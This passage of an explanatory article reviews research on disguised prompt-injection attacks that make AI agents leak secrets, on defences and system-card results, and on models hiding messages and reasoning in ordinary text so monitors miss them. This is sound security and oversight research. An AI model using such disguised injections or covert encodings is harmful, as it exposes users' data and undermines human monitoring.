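The researchers first tried ten kinds of openly worded attack, such as direct commands, instructions hidden in the page's code, and urgent messages posing as the IT department. GPT-4o leaked in none of 200 trials. They then kept the leak the same and changed its description. Some pages presented the secret as a value needed for a routine technical step, and others gave the attacker's address a name like the trusted one. Across eight versions, including a plain control, GPT-4o leaked in 40 percent of trials, and on two versions it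 leaked every time.

They ran both sets of attacks on five other models:

| Model | Openly worded attacks | Disguised attacks |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 0% | 40.0% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 10.0% | 62.5% |
| Qwen2.5 7B | 10.0% | 62.5% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 19.5% | 62.5% |
| Gemma 2 9B | 22.0% | 86.2% |
| Mistral 7B | 26.0% | 27.5% |

Mistral hardly changed. It had resisted the open attacks less than the other models, but only slightly less than Gemma, so its weaker resistance doesn't explain much. Rahman and Kim treat the result as an anomaly.

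The percentages reflect particular sentences more than kinds of attack. When the researchers rewrote each of the two strongest versions five ways, success on GPT-4o averaged 52 percent for one and 14 percent for the other. Individual rewrites of the first ranged from never working to always working. An attacker can try several, though, and Rahman and Kim calculate a 96 percent chance that at least one of three rewrites picked at random would work. But all 130 trials with 13 pages written from scratch failed, so the attack is easy mainly for someone who already has a page that works.

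### Why did the wording matter so much?

Rahman and Kim deleted the policy to test one possible explanation for the leaks, that GPT-4o recognised the secret and consulted its policy but was persuaded by a clever argument to disobey it. Without the policy, GPT-4o still ignored every openly worded attack, and its leak rate under the disguised ones rose only from 31.9 to 38.1 percent. That difference is too small to mean much, since two runs of the same set-up with the policy in place had produced leak rates of 40 and 31.9 percent.

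The policy had almost no effect, so the disguise had little resistance to overcome. GPT-4o seems to have ignored the open commands because they looked out of place and followed the disguised ones because they looked like part of its task.

The page's wording mattered more than the policy. When the researchers edited a page that had caused leaks so that it described the value as a credential, GPT-4o leaked in none of 20 trials. The policy described the value as confidential both before and after the edit. An assistant like this might protect Ines's appointment if a page describes it as medical, but leak it if the page uses a more ordinary term.

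### Acting and judging

The separate detector in Rahman and Kim's experiments was GPT-4o-mini, which only had to decide whether a page contained an instruction to disclose or transmit a secret. It flagged the disguised attacks in all 80 trials and raised no false alarms on clean pages. The same model had leaked in 62.5 percent of the disguised trials when it was the agent, so an inability to recognize the instructions can't explain those leaks.

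An agent reads a page for material for its task, and it tends to follow an instruction that looks like one more step. A judge has no task to finish, and the question it is asked draws attention to the instruction. But this judge also had a list of behaviours to look for, such as encoding or logging the secret.

To test whether the list made the difference, the researchers added the same behaviours to the acting model's policy, with a ban on passing on the secret "in any form". GPT-4o had leaked in 31.9 percent of trials, but with this policy it leaked in none of 120. When the researchers removed only the catch-all phrase, it leaked in 39 of 80 trials, or 48.8 percent. The acting model could avoid leaking, but the list alone gave no measurable protection.

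Rahman and Kim tested the judge only with the list, so they can't say how much of its perfect score came from the hints. In their experiment, the broad ban did not get in the way of the task, which did not require the secret. Ines's assistant could not book her taxi under such a ban. Rahman and Kim conclude that developers should not rely on the acting model's judgement. In their tests, a fine-tuned model still leaked, but restricting where data could go or which part of the system held the secret stopped the disguised leaks.

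Judges without such specific hints do worse. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) tested general-purpose models (7 to 8 billion parameters) that were given the user's request and checked the output of an agent's tools for injections. At a setting that flagged 1 percent of harmless text, the models caught 54 to 78 percent of injections, but one of them caught only 1 percent of those relevant to the user's task.

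The difference between acting and judging also appears in newer models. *Welcome to the Age of Agent Ads* (2026) planted text about an invented concept to influence how agents ranked things such as rental listings. The models could recognise the concept as fake when researchers asked directly, but most almost never mentioned manipulation in their reasoning while ranking. Only Claude Opus 4.8 flagged the manipulation consistently, but it did so in just 6 to 10 percent of cases when the text arrived as a search result.

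### What about ChatGPT and newer models?

Rahman and Kim put some of their pages on the public web and asked ChatGPT to summarise them. ChatGPT did not leak the secret in any of the 48 valid trials, although GPT-4o, accessed through OpenAI's API, had leaked it every time on some of the same attacks.

The researchers found no leaks in 48 trials of ChatGPT, but this doesn't show that it noticed the attacks. It may have been running a different model, or OpenAI may have given it stricter instructions. Other software may have cleaned the page, detected the injection or filtered the reply. In most trials ChatGPT summarised the page and ignored the instruction, and it refused openly on only one kind of page. The comparison with GPT-4o is also uneven, because the researchers looked for the secret only in ChatGPT's reply, whereas GPT-4o could also post it to an outside address. The 48 trials are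 also compatible with a true leak rate of up to 7.4 percent.

GPT-4o dates from 2024, and the other five models are small and about as old. Nobody seems to have published the same test on 2026 models, but two studies come close.

In *Injection-Execution Dissociation*, Leong (2026) tested 29 models from OpenAI, Google and Anthropic, in runs from October. The instruction to leak data was disguised as a company compliance rule about outgoing email. The user asked the agent to look up the company's rules and save them to memory, and three sessions later asked it to draft a project update. Leong counted a leak if the agent sent the update to the attacker's address as well.

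Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview, Gemini 3.5 Flash and GPT-5.1 each leaked data in all ten runs, GPT-5.2 in five of ten and GPT-5.5 in eight of 40. No Anthropic model leaked data in more than one run in ten. Some recent models can therefore still leak data when the leak looks routine, though Leong's set-up made the rule easy to mistake for a real one.

Several of the zero leak counts in Leong's results do not represent refusals. GPT-5.4, GPT-5.6-sol and Claude Haiku 4.5 each leaked in none of 40 runs, but they sent almost no email because the user had asked only for a draft. When Leong supplied the content and asked them to send it, they leaked in 20, 5 and 6 of 20 runs respectively. A content filter ended every Claude Opus 5 session after the agent retrieved the malicious document, before it could decide whether to leak. An earlier round found no leaks in 210 runs, but only because the malicious document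 wasn't among the files the agents could search.

Some Claude models clearly noticed the attack. Opus 4.5 never saved the rule, and in eight of ten runs it wrote that it was declining to. Sonnet 4.6, Sonnet 5 and Opus 4.8 sometimes recorded the attacker's address, but only in a security warning.

Leong also tried judges and stricter instructions. Three leading models flagged the document when their only job was to classify it, but a weaker judge, with 1.5 billion parameters, passed it in all 360 sessions. Four explicit security rules, including one against emailing addresses that the user had not provided, protected none of the open models that leaked reliably without them. The broad ban that worked for Rahman and Kim may therefore fail with other models and tasks.

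The other study, *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026), used an email assistant whose user had not authorised it to send anything. An attack succeeded if the assistant sent an email anyway. This tests whether a model recognises a false claim of permission, rather than whether it protects a secret. Claude Sonnet 4.6 obeyed 0.67 percent of the original attack emails, and its reasoning identified one of them as an injection. Another copy of Sonnet then rewrote the emails repeatedly, which raised the success rate to 96.7 percent. In the rewritten version of the email it had identified, the assistant mistook a forged message for the user's own instruction. The best emails also worked without further changes on GPT-5.4 in 63.3 percent of cases and on Gemini 3 Pro in 92.6 percent.

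Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue that better judgement can't fully solve this problem. Suppose a genuine approval and a forged one look identical to the model, and it has no way to check them. If it acts on such approvals with probability *p*, the forgery succeeds with probability *p* and the genuine request is blocked with probability 1 − *p*, so lowering one error raises the other. The argument applies only to claims that nobody can verify. A system can avoid the trade-off when it can confirm who wrote a message or ask the user.

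*CredLeakBench* (2026) measured how often models leaked credentials in response to phishing requests and how often they refused matching legitimate requests. In one setting, Claude Opus 4.8 leaked credentials in 31.2 percent of the phishing cases and refused 6.6 percent of the legitimate requests. In another, it leaked them in 1.8 percent of the phishing cases but refused 88.3 percent of the legitimate requests. The second result looks more like general caution than an ability to recognise phishing.

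*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) reports on a public competition in which 464 participants made 272,000 attempts to attack 13 leading models. To succeed, they had to make the agent do something harmful and leave no sign of it in its final answer. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5 percent for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 percent for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

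### Can a model register an attack without acting on it?

As a model processes text, each of its layers produces a long list of numbers called a hidden state. In *Your Agentic LLMs Secretly Encode Indirect Prompt-Injection Exposure in Hidden States* (August 2026), Dong, Liu and colleagues examined whether these numbers can be used to tell that a model has just read a prompt injection. They ran eight open models, with between 2 billion and 2.8 trillion parameters, through simulated banking, travel, messaging and office tasks.

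For each model, they trained probes, which are simple formulas that compute a weighted sum of the numbers in a hidden state. Each probe used the state just before the model started writing to predict whether the latest tool result contained an injection. The correct answer did not depend on whether the model went on to obey the injection.

The researchers tested the probes on tasks, attacks and agent instructions that were not in their training data. The best probe for each model scored between 0.934 and 0.979. This score is the chance that a probe ranks a random turn with an injection above a random turn without one, so guessing would score 0.5. The scores may be slightly too high, because the researchers used the test results to pick the best layer for each model.

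The models' behaviour was much less reliable. The researchers used GPT-5.4 to classify the written reasoning and actions of Qwen3-8B, the most easily attacked of the eight, at 634 turns where the probe had correctly detected an injection. Qwen3-8B never considered the risk in 30.9 percent of these turns, recognised it but did not counter it in 47.0 percent, and made a defensive judgement and acted safely in 22.1 percent. At least for this small model in difficult tests, it was more common to recognise the risk and not counter it than to miss it.

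Next, whenever the probe detected an injection, Dong and colleagues started the model's reasoning with a short reminder to ignore tasks from untrusted content. The success rate of attacks fell from 47.2 to 2.9 percent on Qwen3-8B and from 34.6 percent to zero on Qwen3.5-27B, with little harm to ordinary tasks. In some of the remaining failures, the model reasoned correctly about what belonged to the user's task but still carried out the attacker's request.

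A probe can show that a model's hidden state contains information, but not that the model uses it, so these results do not establish that the models knew they were under attack. When Qwen3-8B only read transcripts from other models, its probe detected injections about as well as those models' own probes did. The signal may therefore reflect the text itself more than any awareness of being a target.

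Most of the attacks were also openly worded. The probes stayed accurate on rewritten attacks that had succeeded, but those rewrites weren't designed to evade them. The study doesn't show whether closed models, whose hidden states outsiders can't inspect, carry the same signal.

Other studies have also found models that notice an injection and still follow it. In *The Window Is in the Reasoning* (2026), agents discussed the injection early in most of the runs where they complied and in nearly half of the runs where they resisted, so an early mention is no sign that an agent will refuse. Leong found that OpenAI models reviewing code often described an instruction as suspicious and carried it out anyway, but this result comes from keyword matching, and Leong treats it as an upper bound.

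A model can also resist an attack without noticing it. *Depth-Dependent Indirect Prompt Injection in Tool-Calling ReAct Agents* (2026) distinguishes an agent that explicitly rejects an instruction from one that passes over it because it doesn't fit the task. The second kind of agent is not safe from disguised attacks like Rahman and Kim's, which are designed to fit the task.

### What do models meet on the web?

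Most of these experiments used attacks written by researchers. For *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya, Zhang and colleagues (2026) instead searched 1.2 billion web addresses and two catalogues of internet servers for injections that others had planted. Their April 2026 survey confirmed 15,387. Many were meant to disrupt AI systems, protect content from them or expose bots, and only 13 were meant to steal data. Nine of those targeted the model's hidden instructions, and four targeted other secrets.

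The low number is reassuring only about crude attacks. The survey searched for 3,963 known phrases, so it would probably have missed a leak disguised as routine technical work. It could also have missed pages that show their instructions only to AI agents.

The researchers then took 100 of the injections and asked 13 models to summarise the pages containing them, in four formats. Small models followed the injected instruction in 4.2 percent of runs, and the two closed models, including GPT-5.4, did so in 0.6 percent. The highest rate was 8 percent, for small models reading plain text. Plain text was the riskiest format, perhaps because it removes the page code that shows an instruction was hidden from human readers. The longer formats look safer partly because some models could not process them; about a quarter of the runs on raw server responses ended in an error.

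Models usually resisted the injection without mentioning it. The closed models pointed it out in 25.1 percent of runs and the small ones in 4.8 percent. In roughly 70 percent of all 5,200 runs, the model neither complied nor gave a warning, and no error occurred. In some of those runs, the model may have noticed the injection and said nothing, since the task was only to write a summary. In six runs, a model recognised the malicious instruction and still followed it, for example by switching to German.

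## How much does training against prompt injection help?

The models in the experiments above mostly resisted crude injections but more often followed those that looked like part of their task. Developers now train models specifically to resist injections. This training rewards a model for sticking to the user's request, so it may not teach the model to recognise a covert channel. But it can still stop the leak, which depends on the model following the planted instruction.

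### How developers train models to resist

One method trains the model to rank instructions by their source. Standing instructions from the company that built the application come first, then the user's requests, then text that tools bring in from web pages and emails. OpenAI calls this ranking the instruction hierarchy. In training, the model gets examples in which a lower-ranked source contradicts a higher-ranked one, and earns a reward for obeying the higher one. It also needs examples in which the two are compatible, such as a user asking for a shorter answer, or it could learn to ignore users.

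OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) distinguishes two kinds of attack on this ranking. In a direct attack, the user tries to override the company's instructions. In an indirect attack, the kind Ines faces, a third party tries to redirect the agent through instructions in their content.

The model learns the ranking as a tendency, and nothing in the model enforces it. The ranking also works only if the model recognises the planted text as an instruction from the page. GPT-4o apparently failed to do this with Rahman and Kim's disguised attacks.

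SecAlign, a method published in 2025, uses preference training, in which a model learns from pairs of answers to the same input. The input contains a legitimate request and data with an injected instruction. One answer carries out the request and the other obeys the injection. Training makes the first answer more likely and the second less likely. SecAlign also gives the model a separate input channel for untrusted text, so an application can mark a web page as data.

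Both methods need attacks to train on, and people can write only a limited number. OpenAI therefore trains a second model to invent them, using reinforcement learning, which strengthens whatever behavior earns a reward. An attacker rewarded only for success may keep repeating one trick. *Diverse and Effective Red Teaming with Auto-generated Rewards and Multi-step Reinforcement Learning* (2024) describes a model that writes attacks, including prompt injections, and is rewarded both for success and for differing from its past attempts.

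In December 2025 OpenAI described a more elaborate version for Atlas, its web browser with a built-in agent (OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025)). It works as follows:

1. The attacking model drafts an injection, such as a malicious email.
2. A simulator runs the browser agent on a task in which it reads the email, and returns a full record of the agent's reasoning and actions.
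3. The attacker revises the email in light of that record, and repeats the cycle several times before settling on a final version.
4. Reinforcement learning rewards the attacker if the final version works.
5. OpenAI trains the browser agent on the successful attacks, concentrating on those it currently fails to resist, and releases the improved agent.

The attacker has an advantage over outsiders because it can read the agent's reasoning, which OpenAI doesn't publish. In one attack it found, a planted email contained instructions for the agent to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent read the email and sent the letter.

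OpenAI trained GPT-Red, the successor to this attacker, alongside a group of defending models. GPT-Red was rewarded for making a defender fail, and the defenders were rewarded for resisting the attack and finishing their original task. As the defenders improved, GPT-Red had to find stronger and more varied attacks. OpenAI then used it to write injections for training GPT-5.6 (OpenAI's *GPT‑Red* (2026)). An early version of GPT-Red found a family of direct attacks that worked on GPT-5.1 more than 95 percent of the time. These attacks work on GPT-5.6 Sol less than 10 percent of the time.

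### What the system cards report

Developers publish a system card with a new model to report on its safety tests. The figures in these cards are hard to compare because an attack's success rate depends on the attacker's goal, the number of attempts allowed, and whether the attacker could adapt.

GPT-6 Astra, which OpenAI released in September 2026, is more robust to injection than GPT-5.6 Sol, but its written reasoning is harder to monitor, according to OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026). On OpenAI's own test of indirect attacks, which uses GPT-Red, Sol resisted 96.23 percent of attacks and Astra resisted 99.79 percent. These are averages per query, and OpenAI doesn't state how many attempts the attacker had at each target or whether it could adapt to Astra's replies.

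Astra did less well on a benchmark from the security company Gray Swan. Attacks from a fixed set of 1,810 succeeded within 15 attempts in an estimated 8.5 percent of cases, down from 27.0 percent for Sol. The extra attempts explain only part of the gap between 0.21 and 8.5 percent, since 15 independent attempts with a 0.21 percent chance each would produce at least one success about 3 percent of the time. The rest is probably because Gray Swan chose attacks that had worked on several models.

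The benchmark draws on public competitions like the one in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, whose authors include staff at OpenAI, Anthropic, Meta, and British and American government institutes. It is an outside test, but the companies helped design it.

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 reports results on nearly the same benchmark, with 1,804 attacks in 37 scenarios. Attacks succeeded within 15 attempts in 1.0 percent of cases against Fable 5.1, 4.8 percent against Claude Opus 5 and 6.5 percent against Fable 5. Of the other companies' models in the comparison, Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash did best, at 9.2 percent, and most of the rest fell between 24 and 53 percent. Anthropic released Fable 5.1's successor in November (*Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026)).

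A fixed set of attacks favours newer models. Models that were targets in the competitions do worse on the benchmark because people tailored attacks to them, so Anthropic leaves them out. But the remaining models still face attacks that nobody tailored to them. Anthropic warns in the same card that such tests can give a false sense of security, so it also uses Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan.

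The table shows how Fable 5 and Fable 5.1 did on each test without Anthropic's dedicated protections against injection. The Gray Swan row gives the chance that at least one of 15 injection attempts succeeds. The other rows give the share of all attempts that succeeded.

| Test | Attempts per scenario | Attacker | Fable 5 | Fable 5.1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gray Swan benchmark | 15 | Fixed attacks | 6.5% | 1.0% |
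| Coding | 200 | Trained on the test scenarios | 9.70% | 9.26% |
| Coding, stronger attacker | 200 | Trained for longer on the same scenarios | 86.87% | 56.87% |
| Controlling a computer screen | 200 | Trained on the test scenarios | 2.50% | 0.07% |
| Web browsing | 10 | Fixed attacks, first built against Claude Opus 4.7 | 6.04% | 2.64% |

The two coding rows use the same 40 scenarios and the same number of attempts, so the difference comes from the attacker. The first version of Shade broke Fable 5.1 at least once in 31 scenarios, and the stronger version in 38. The difference is clearest for Opus 5, whose rate rose from 2.68 percent with the first version to 90.93 percent with the stronger one. The first figure alone would have made Opus 5 look fairly safe.

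Anthropic regards the stronger attacker as a stress test, because a real attacker would rarely know the exact scenario or get 200 tries without being caught. Gray Swan trained the first attacker against earlier Claude models and ran it unchanged on the new ones, so it had learned the scenarios but had not adapted to the new models. Research on adaptive attackers generally finds that defences that hold against fixed attacks often fail once the attacker can adjust to them.

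The coding figures for Fable 5.1 also mostly measure a different model. Anthropic runs a filter that sends requests that look like hacking to an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, which answers them instead. In the test with the stronger attacker, Opus 4.8 handled about 64 percent of requests, and attacks succeeded on nearly nine in ten of those. No attack succeeded on the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself. This result may overstate Fable 5.1's resistance, because the filter decided which requests it received and may have diverted the most aggressive attacks.

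More capable models do not always resist better, either. When it could reason before acting, Claude Sonnet 5, which Anthropic ranks below its Opus models in capability, had the lowest attack success rates of the four Claude models, at 0.3 and 19.47 percent in the two coding tests and 0.28 percent in web browsing. Without reasoning, its rate against the stronger coding attacker roughly doubled to 40.30 percent.

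Anthropic adds separate checks in its products. One inspects tool results for injections before the model acts on them, and it cut the stronger attacker's success rate against Fable 5.1 from 56.87 to 12.80 percent. In the browsing test, this check and another that blocks dangerous actions together stopped every attack on Fable 5.1. These gains come from software around the model, so they aren't evidence about its training.

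### Which tests measure data leaving?

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) makes the most direct claim that training stops data theft. It reports that attacks on ChatGPT most often try to make it send secret information from a conversation to a third party, and that in most cases the company knows of, the attack fails "because our safety training causes the agent to refuse."

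This is relevant evidence from the company that sees the most attacks on ChatGPT, but it is hard to weigh. OpenAI doesn't give the number of cases or explain how it distinguished agents that refused the instruction from agents that never took it up. It can also count only the attacks it knows about, which are less likely to include successful thefts that leave no trace. The same article reproduces an attack that outside researchers reported in 2025, which worked half the time in testing. OpenAI also has a separate check, called Safe Url, for when the agent is persuaded. It looks for information from the conversation that is about to be sent to a third party, then either asks the user to confirm or blocks the transfer.

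Few published figures cover data theft alone. The Gray Swan benchmark includes theft of private data, but both companies' headline results combine it with destroyed data, compromised systems and unauthorised payments.

The Astra card does count data leaks separately in one set of tests. The models worked in realistic email, messaging, sales and similar applications, where ambiguous instructions, similar-looking files and complicated permissions made mistakes likely, though every task had a safe way to proceed. Astra leaked data in 4.3 percent of cases and GPT-5.6 Sol in 14.1 percent. OpenAI then added the policy that applies by default for real users, which covers when the models should stop and ask for approval. Sol's rate fell to 8.8 percent, while Astra's stayed about the same at 4.5 percent.

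OpenAI doesn't describe planted instructions in these tasks, so they seem to measure carelessness with data rather than resistance to an attacker. Carelessness still matters for someone like Ines, whose assistant could send her appointment to the wrong person without any attacker. Astra was much more careful than Sol, but the approval policy didn't help it further, perhaps because Astra didn't recognise the remaining leaks as something to ask about.

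Another test in the card is closer to a prompt injection. OpenAI gave agents a browsing task and a simulated message board containing instructions to act improperly, for instance by disclosing private information or approving illicit access. Sol engaged with the board in 84 percent of runs and followed its instructions in 52 percent. Astra engaged with it in 27 percent and never followed the instructions. OpenAI does not report disclosures of private data separately from other misbehaviour, and it had repeatedly revised the test to provoke misbehaviour.

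OpenAI also tested GPT-Red on ten data-theft scenarios it had not trained on, in which the target was a coding agent running on GPT-5.4 mini. GPT-Red stole data in more of them than GPT-5.5, which was only prompted to attack. This test shows that training improved the attacker, but OpenAI did not run it on a defender before and after training.

### Does resistance carry over to new attacks?

A model can do well on a prompt injection test because it has learned to resist injections in general, or because it was trained on similar ones. In December 2025, OpenAI reported that GPT-5.2 scored nearly perfectly on two injection tests, one with attacks in simulated email and one with attacks in tool call results. Both tests came from the same data as the training examples, and OpenAI acknowledges in its *Update to GPT-5 System Card* (2025) that they "don't represent a model's ability to generalize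 to new attacks."

Leong's fake compliance rule was probably unlike anything in that data, and GPT-5.2 leaked in half its runs. The rule also sometimes worked on GPT-5.6 Sol, which OpenAI had trained against GPT-Red. This was a hard test, but real attackers would also try to make their instructions look legitimate.

OpenAI's newer tests are better separated from training. OpenAI tested GPT-5.6 Sol against GPT-Red's attacks in environments it had kept out of training, and Sol failed on only 0.05 percent of direct attacks. But GPT-Red had also written the attacks that Sol trained on, so the test attacks may have resembled those in training. Anthropic also kept its 110 browsing scenarios out of training.

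Human testers may also miss attacks that a trained model finds. When OpenAI ran a copy of the public competition's scenarios against GPT-5.1, GPT-Red succeeded in 84 percent of them and human participants in 13 percent. GPT-Red also attacked an AI agent that runs a vending machine in OpenAI's office. It had only partial knowledge of the system and developed its attacks on a simulation first. It then made the live agent cut the price of an expensive item to 50 cents, offer a newly ordered item worth over $100 for the same price, and cancel another customer's order.

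System cards can't show how much of the improvement between two models came from injection training, because developers change many other things at the same time. SecAlign allows a cleaner comparison because researchers can test the same Llama model with and without it. Rahman and Kim did this with the 8-billion-parameter version. They first tried a standard injection that told the model to ignore its instructions and print a particular phrase. The ordinary model followed the injection in all 20 trials and the SecAlign model in none, so the training worked against the kind of attack it was designed for.

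They then made the model an agent with tools and a secret to protect. The agent received its policy and task in the trusted channel, and the web page in SecAlign's channel for untrusted text. Under the disguised attacks, the SecAlign model leaked the secret in 32.5 percent of trials. The ordinary model, which had no special training, leaked it in 38.8 percent of trials when the page had its own channel and in 21.2 percent when it received everything together.

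These three rates show that SecAlign came nowhere near stopping the leak. They don't show that it made the leak worse, because each comes from a single run, and two runs of the same set-up in another of Rahman and Kim's experiments differed by about 8 points. When the attack asked for the secret in a coded form, the SecAlign model leaked in 16.7 percent of trials. The ordinary model leaked in none when it received everything together and in 6.7 percent when the page had its own channel, but there were probably too few trials to conclude much from these differences.

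SecAlign's developers trained it to handle text, but Rahman and Kim used it to control tools. They accept that this was outside its intended use and conclude only that its protection did not carry over to guarding a secret in an agent. The test is still a fair check on what a developer might expect, since a developer who sees a perfect score on standard injections could easily assume that an agent built on the model would be safe too. The result also comes from one small model, and OpenAI's training covers tool use and a far larger range of attacks.

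### What does a one percent success rate mean?

If each attempt succeeds independently with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is 1 − (1 − *p*)<sup>*n*</sup>. An attacker who tries 100 times with a 1 percent success rate therefore has about a 63 percent chance of getting through at least once.

In practice, attempts are seldom independent. A model that recognises an email as an attack will probably also recognise a slightly altered copy, and some tasks are easier to attack than others. In Anthropic's test of controlling a computer screen, all five successful attacks on Opus 5 came in one of the 14 scenarios, whereas independent attempts at the same overall rate would be expected to break about four. Against Fable 5.1, the first coding attacker succeeded in 9.26 percent of its attempts. If those successes had been spread evenly and independently, they would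 have broken all 40 scenarios, but nine survived all 200 attempts.

Claude Opus 4.6, an older model, illustrates the same point. VentureBeat reported that attacks on it in a computer-use test succeeded 17.8 percent of the time on the first attempt, and that the chance of a breach reached 78.6 percent by the 200th. If the attempts had been independent, a breach would have been practically certain long before then.

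So the formula can overstate what an attacker gains by repeating similar attacks. It can also understate the danger from an attacker who learns from each failure, whose later attempts are more likely to succeed. The formula also leaves out the extra chances that repeated attempts give the defender to notice and block the attacker.

An attacker who doesn't care about Ines in particular can instead send the same email to a thousand inboxes and reach every agent that summarises them, as Anthropic points out. Those attempts are far from independent, since many of the agents will run on the same model. If the email fails on one of those agents, it may fail on nearly all of them, but if it works, it could expose hundreds of people before anyone notices.

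### The cost in refused tasks

An attack success rate means little unless we also know whether the model still does its work. OpenAI makes this point about GPT-Red, and rewards defenders in training for completing the task as well as for resisting attacks. OpenAI reports that normal capabilities were unaffected and that it tested for unnecessary refusals, but it gives no figures. Anthropic's prompt injection results for Fable 5.1 don't include a rate of wrongly refused tasks either.

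Such refusals could well happen, because people often want an assistant to follow instructions in someone else's text. Ines might forward a letter from her clinic and ask the assistant to do what it says, such as filling in a form and sending it back with her date of birth. A model trained to ignore every instruction in an email wouldn't help her. The assistant has to understand that she has authorised the clinic's instructions, but not an extra line asking for her bank details.

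In one *CredLeakBench* setting, Claude Opus 4.8 leaked few credentials but also refused most legitimate requests, so a low leak rate can be misleading. The result doesn't show how much injection training reduces a model's usefulness, because models with and without that training weren't compared.

The companies publish more about wrongly refused requests from users, which is a different problem. Anthropic reports that Claude Sonnet 5 refuses malicious coding requests much more reliably than Sonnet 4.6 but also refuses acceptable ones more often. OpenAI reports that Astra does better than its predecessors on both measures. Ines can't tell from either result whether an assistant that has learned to distrust web pages will still follow the clinic's letter.

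## How well can models hide messages in ordinary text, and do they refuse to?

A message hidden in ordinary wording gets past most of the defences described so far, because it needs no suspicious address or unusual character. The model must be both able and willing to write such a message. Researchers have measured the ability in detail, but they have mostly recorded refusals in passing, when a refusal disrupted an experiment.

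### Passing a message and reasoning in secret

In the tests of messaging and steganographic reasoning, Schulz and colleagues gave models an ordinary question and a rule for recording numbers in surface features of the answer. In the messaging tests, the prompt supplied the numbers. In the steganographic reasoning tests, the model had to work them out one at a time as it wrote, using the ones it had already hidden as notes. The encoded reasoning tests had no ordinary question, and the model wrote only its reasoning, in encoded form.

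One simple calculation was to keep a running total. Another was to follow a ball under five cups as the cups changed places. The researchers added the cups because a model can do short sums without writing anything down, so a correct total doesn't show that it used its hidden notes. Mathematicians expect that no model of this kind can follow the cups through a long enough sequence without notes. The researchers also switched off the models' separate chain of thought, so any written working had to go into the answer.

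The monitor, GPT-5-mini, was given the question and the answer but not the rule, and rated from 1 to 10 how much the answer contained things that didn't belong. Schulz and colleagues counted a score of 3 or less as covert. In their checks, at least 94 percent of normal answers scored that low, compared with at most 4 percent of answers with numbers or unrelated words openly added. A low score means only that nothing looked out of place to a reader without the rule. A monitor given the rule could read the message directly.

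The prompting tests covered eight leading models, none from Anthropic. Several combinations of model and rule hid a ten-number message both accurately and covertly. Gemini 3.5 Flash, for example, recorded 87 percent of the numbers correctly under one rule, with an average suspicion score of 1.2. When the models also had to calculate the numbers, almost no combination was both accurate and covert. The models typically got the first few numbers right and guessed the rest. Schulz and colleagues think the models worked out the first few steps internally and then wrote down the results, so they were using the hidden text only to send a message, not to calculate.

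GPT-5.5 could hide a given message when told only the rule, and it learned encoded reasoning from a few worked examples. It never managed to combine the two, even when the number of examples was increased to five.

The researchers then used reinforcement learning on Qwen3.6, an open model with 35 billion parameters. They rewarded it for each correct hidden number and reduced the reward if the monitor rated the text suspicious. The model learned encoded reasoning almost immediately and messaging within about 100 training steps. Steganographic reasoning, which combines the two, was stuck at 69 percent accuracy after 760 steps, on a task where guessing scores 50 percent. The monitor's penalty can't explain the difference, because messaging carried the same penalty. Results were similar when the model could invent its own rule, with 98 or 99 percent accuracy on encoded reasoning and messaging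 within 140 steps, and between 54 and 59 percent on steganographic reasoning.

### What does fine-tuning add?

Reinforcement learning can fail because the model never produces the right behaviour, so there is nothing to reward. Supervised fine-tuning avoids this by training the model on finished examples. Schulz and colleagues fine-tuned six open models until the models recorded 95 percent of the hidden numbers correctly. Encoded reasoning took at most 200 steps on every model. The table shows the steps for the other two skills.

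| Model | Running total: messaging | Running total: steganographic reasoning | Cups: messaging | Cups: steganographic reasoning |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.6-35B | 500 | 10,200 | 700 | not within 1,400 |
| Nemotron-3-Super | 700 | 6,800 | 500 | 2,300 |
| gpt-oss-120B | 1,000 | not within 10,000 | 800 | 1,900 |
| Inkling-Small | 1,100 | 3,000 | 300 | 900 |
| Lightning-30B | 2,100 | not within 21,000 | 1,900 | not within 19,000 |
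| Inkling | 1,000 | not within 2,000 | not tested | not tested |

Where models learned steganographic reasoning, they needed 2.4 to 20 times as many training steps as they did to learn messaging. In five of the eleven pairings of model and task, the model did not learn steganographic reasoning before training stopped.

The experiment shows that steganographic reasoning is slow to learn, but some of the models in those five failed runs might have learned it with more training. On the running total, Qwen3.6 got no complete sequence right until step 4,300 and fewer than 10 percent right until about step 9,500, then passed 90 percent within roughly 900 more steps. The researchers stopped three of the failed runs at ten times the model's messaging budget and the other two at only twice that budget. If they had stopped Qwen3.6 at ten times its messaging budget, they would have recorded another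 failure.

### The exception

Steganographic reasoning was much easier in one task, where the model had to solve a packing puzzle by trying many random combinations of items and reporting the best one that stayed under a weight limit. Since the combinations were supposed to be random, the model could use its choices to record hidden numbers without making the answer worse.

With prompting alone, GPT-5.5 kept a hidden running record correct through all 24 steps. It got the final answer to the hidden calculation right 92 percent of the time, compared with 46 percent (no better than guessing) when it had to answer without any written working. The other eight models in this test made errors in the record, most of them within the first few steps.

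Reinforcement learning also worked here, taking Qwen3.6 from chance to 100 percent in about 20 steps. That run rewarded every hidden number, which no ordinary training would do, so the researchers repeated it with a reward only for the final answer. The 35-billion-parameter model stayed at chance for all 40 steps. A 397-billion-parameter version of Qwen3.5 reached 100 percent by step 30, and its hidden notes became fully accurate although nothing rewarded them. The prompt still described the rule, so the model did not invent the method. Its answers were fairly conspicuous, with an average suspicion score of 5.2, but the score was still falling when training ended.

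A model could still have calculated the answer internally without using the notes it wrote. To test this, Schulz and colleagues changed one hidden number partway through and let the model continue. In two of the packing runs, 84 and 71 percent of the later numbers carried the error forward, so the models were mostly using their own notes. Among models fine-tuned on the other tasks, some carried the error forward and others lost track of the calculation, but after the first three or four numbers none reliably returned to the correct sequence.

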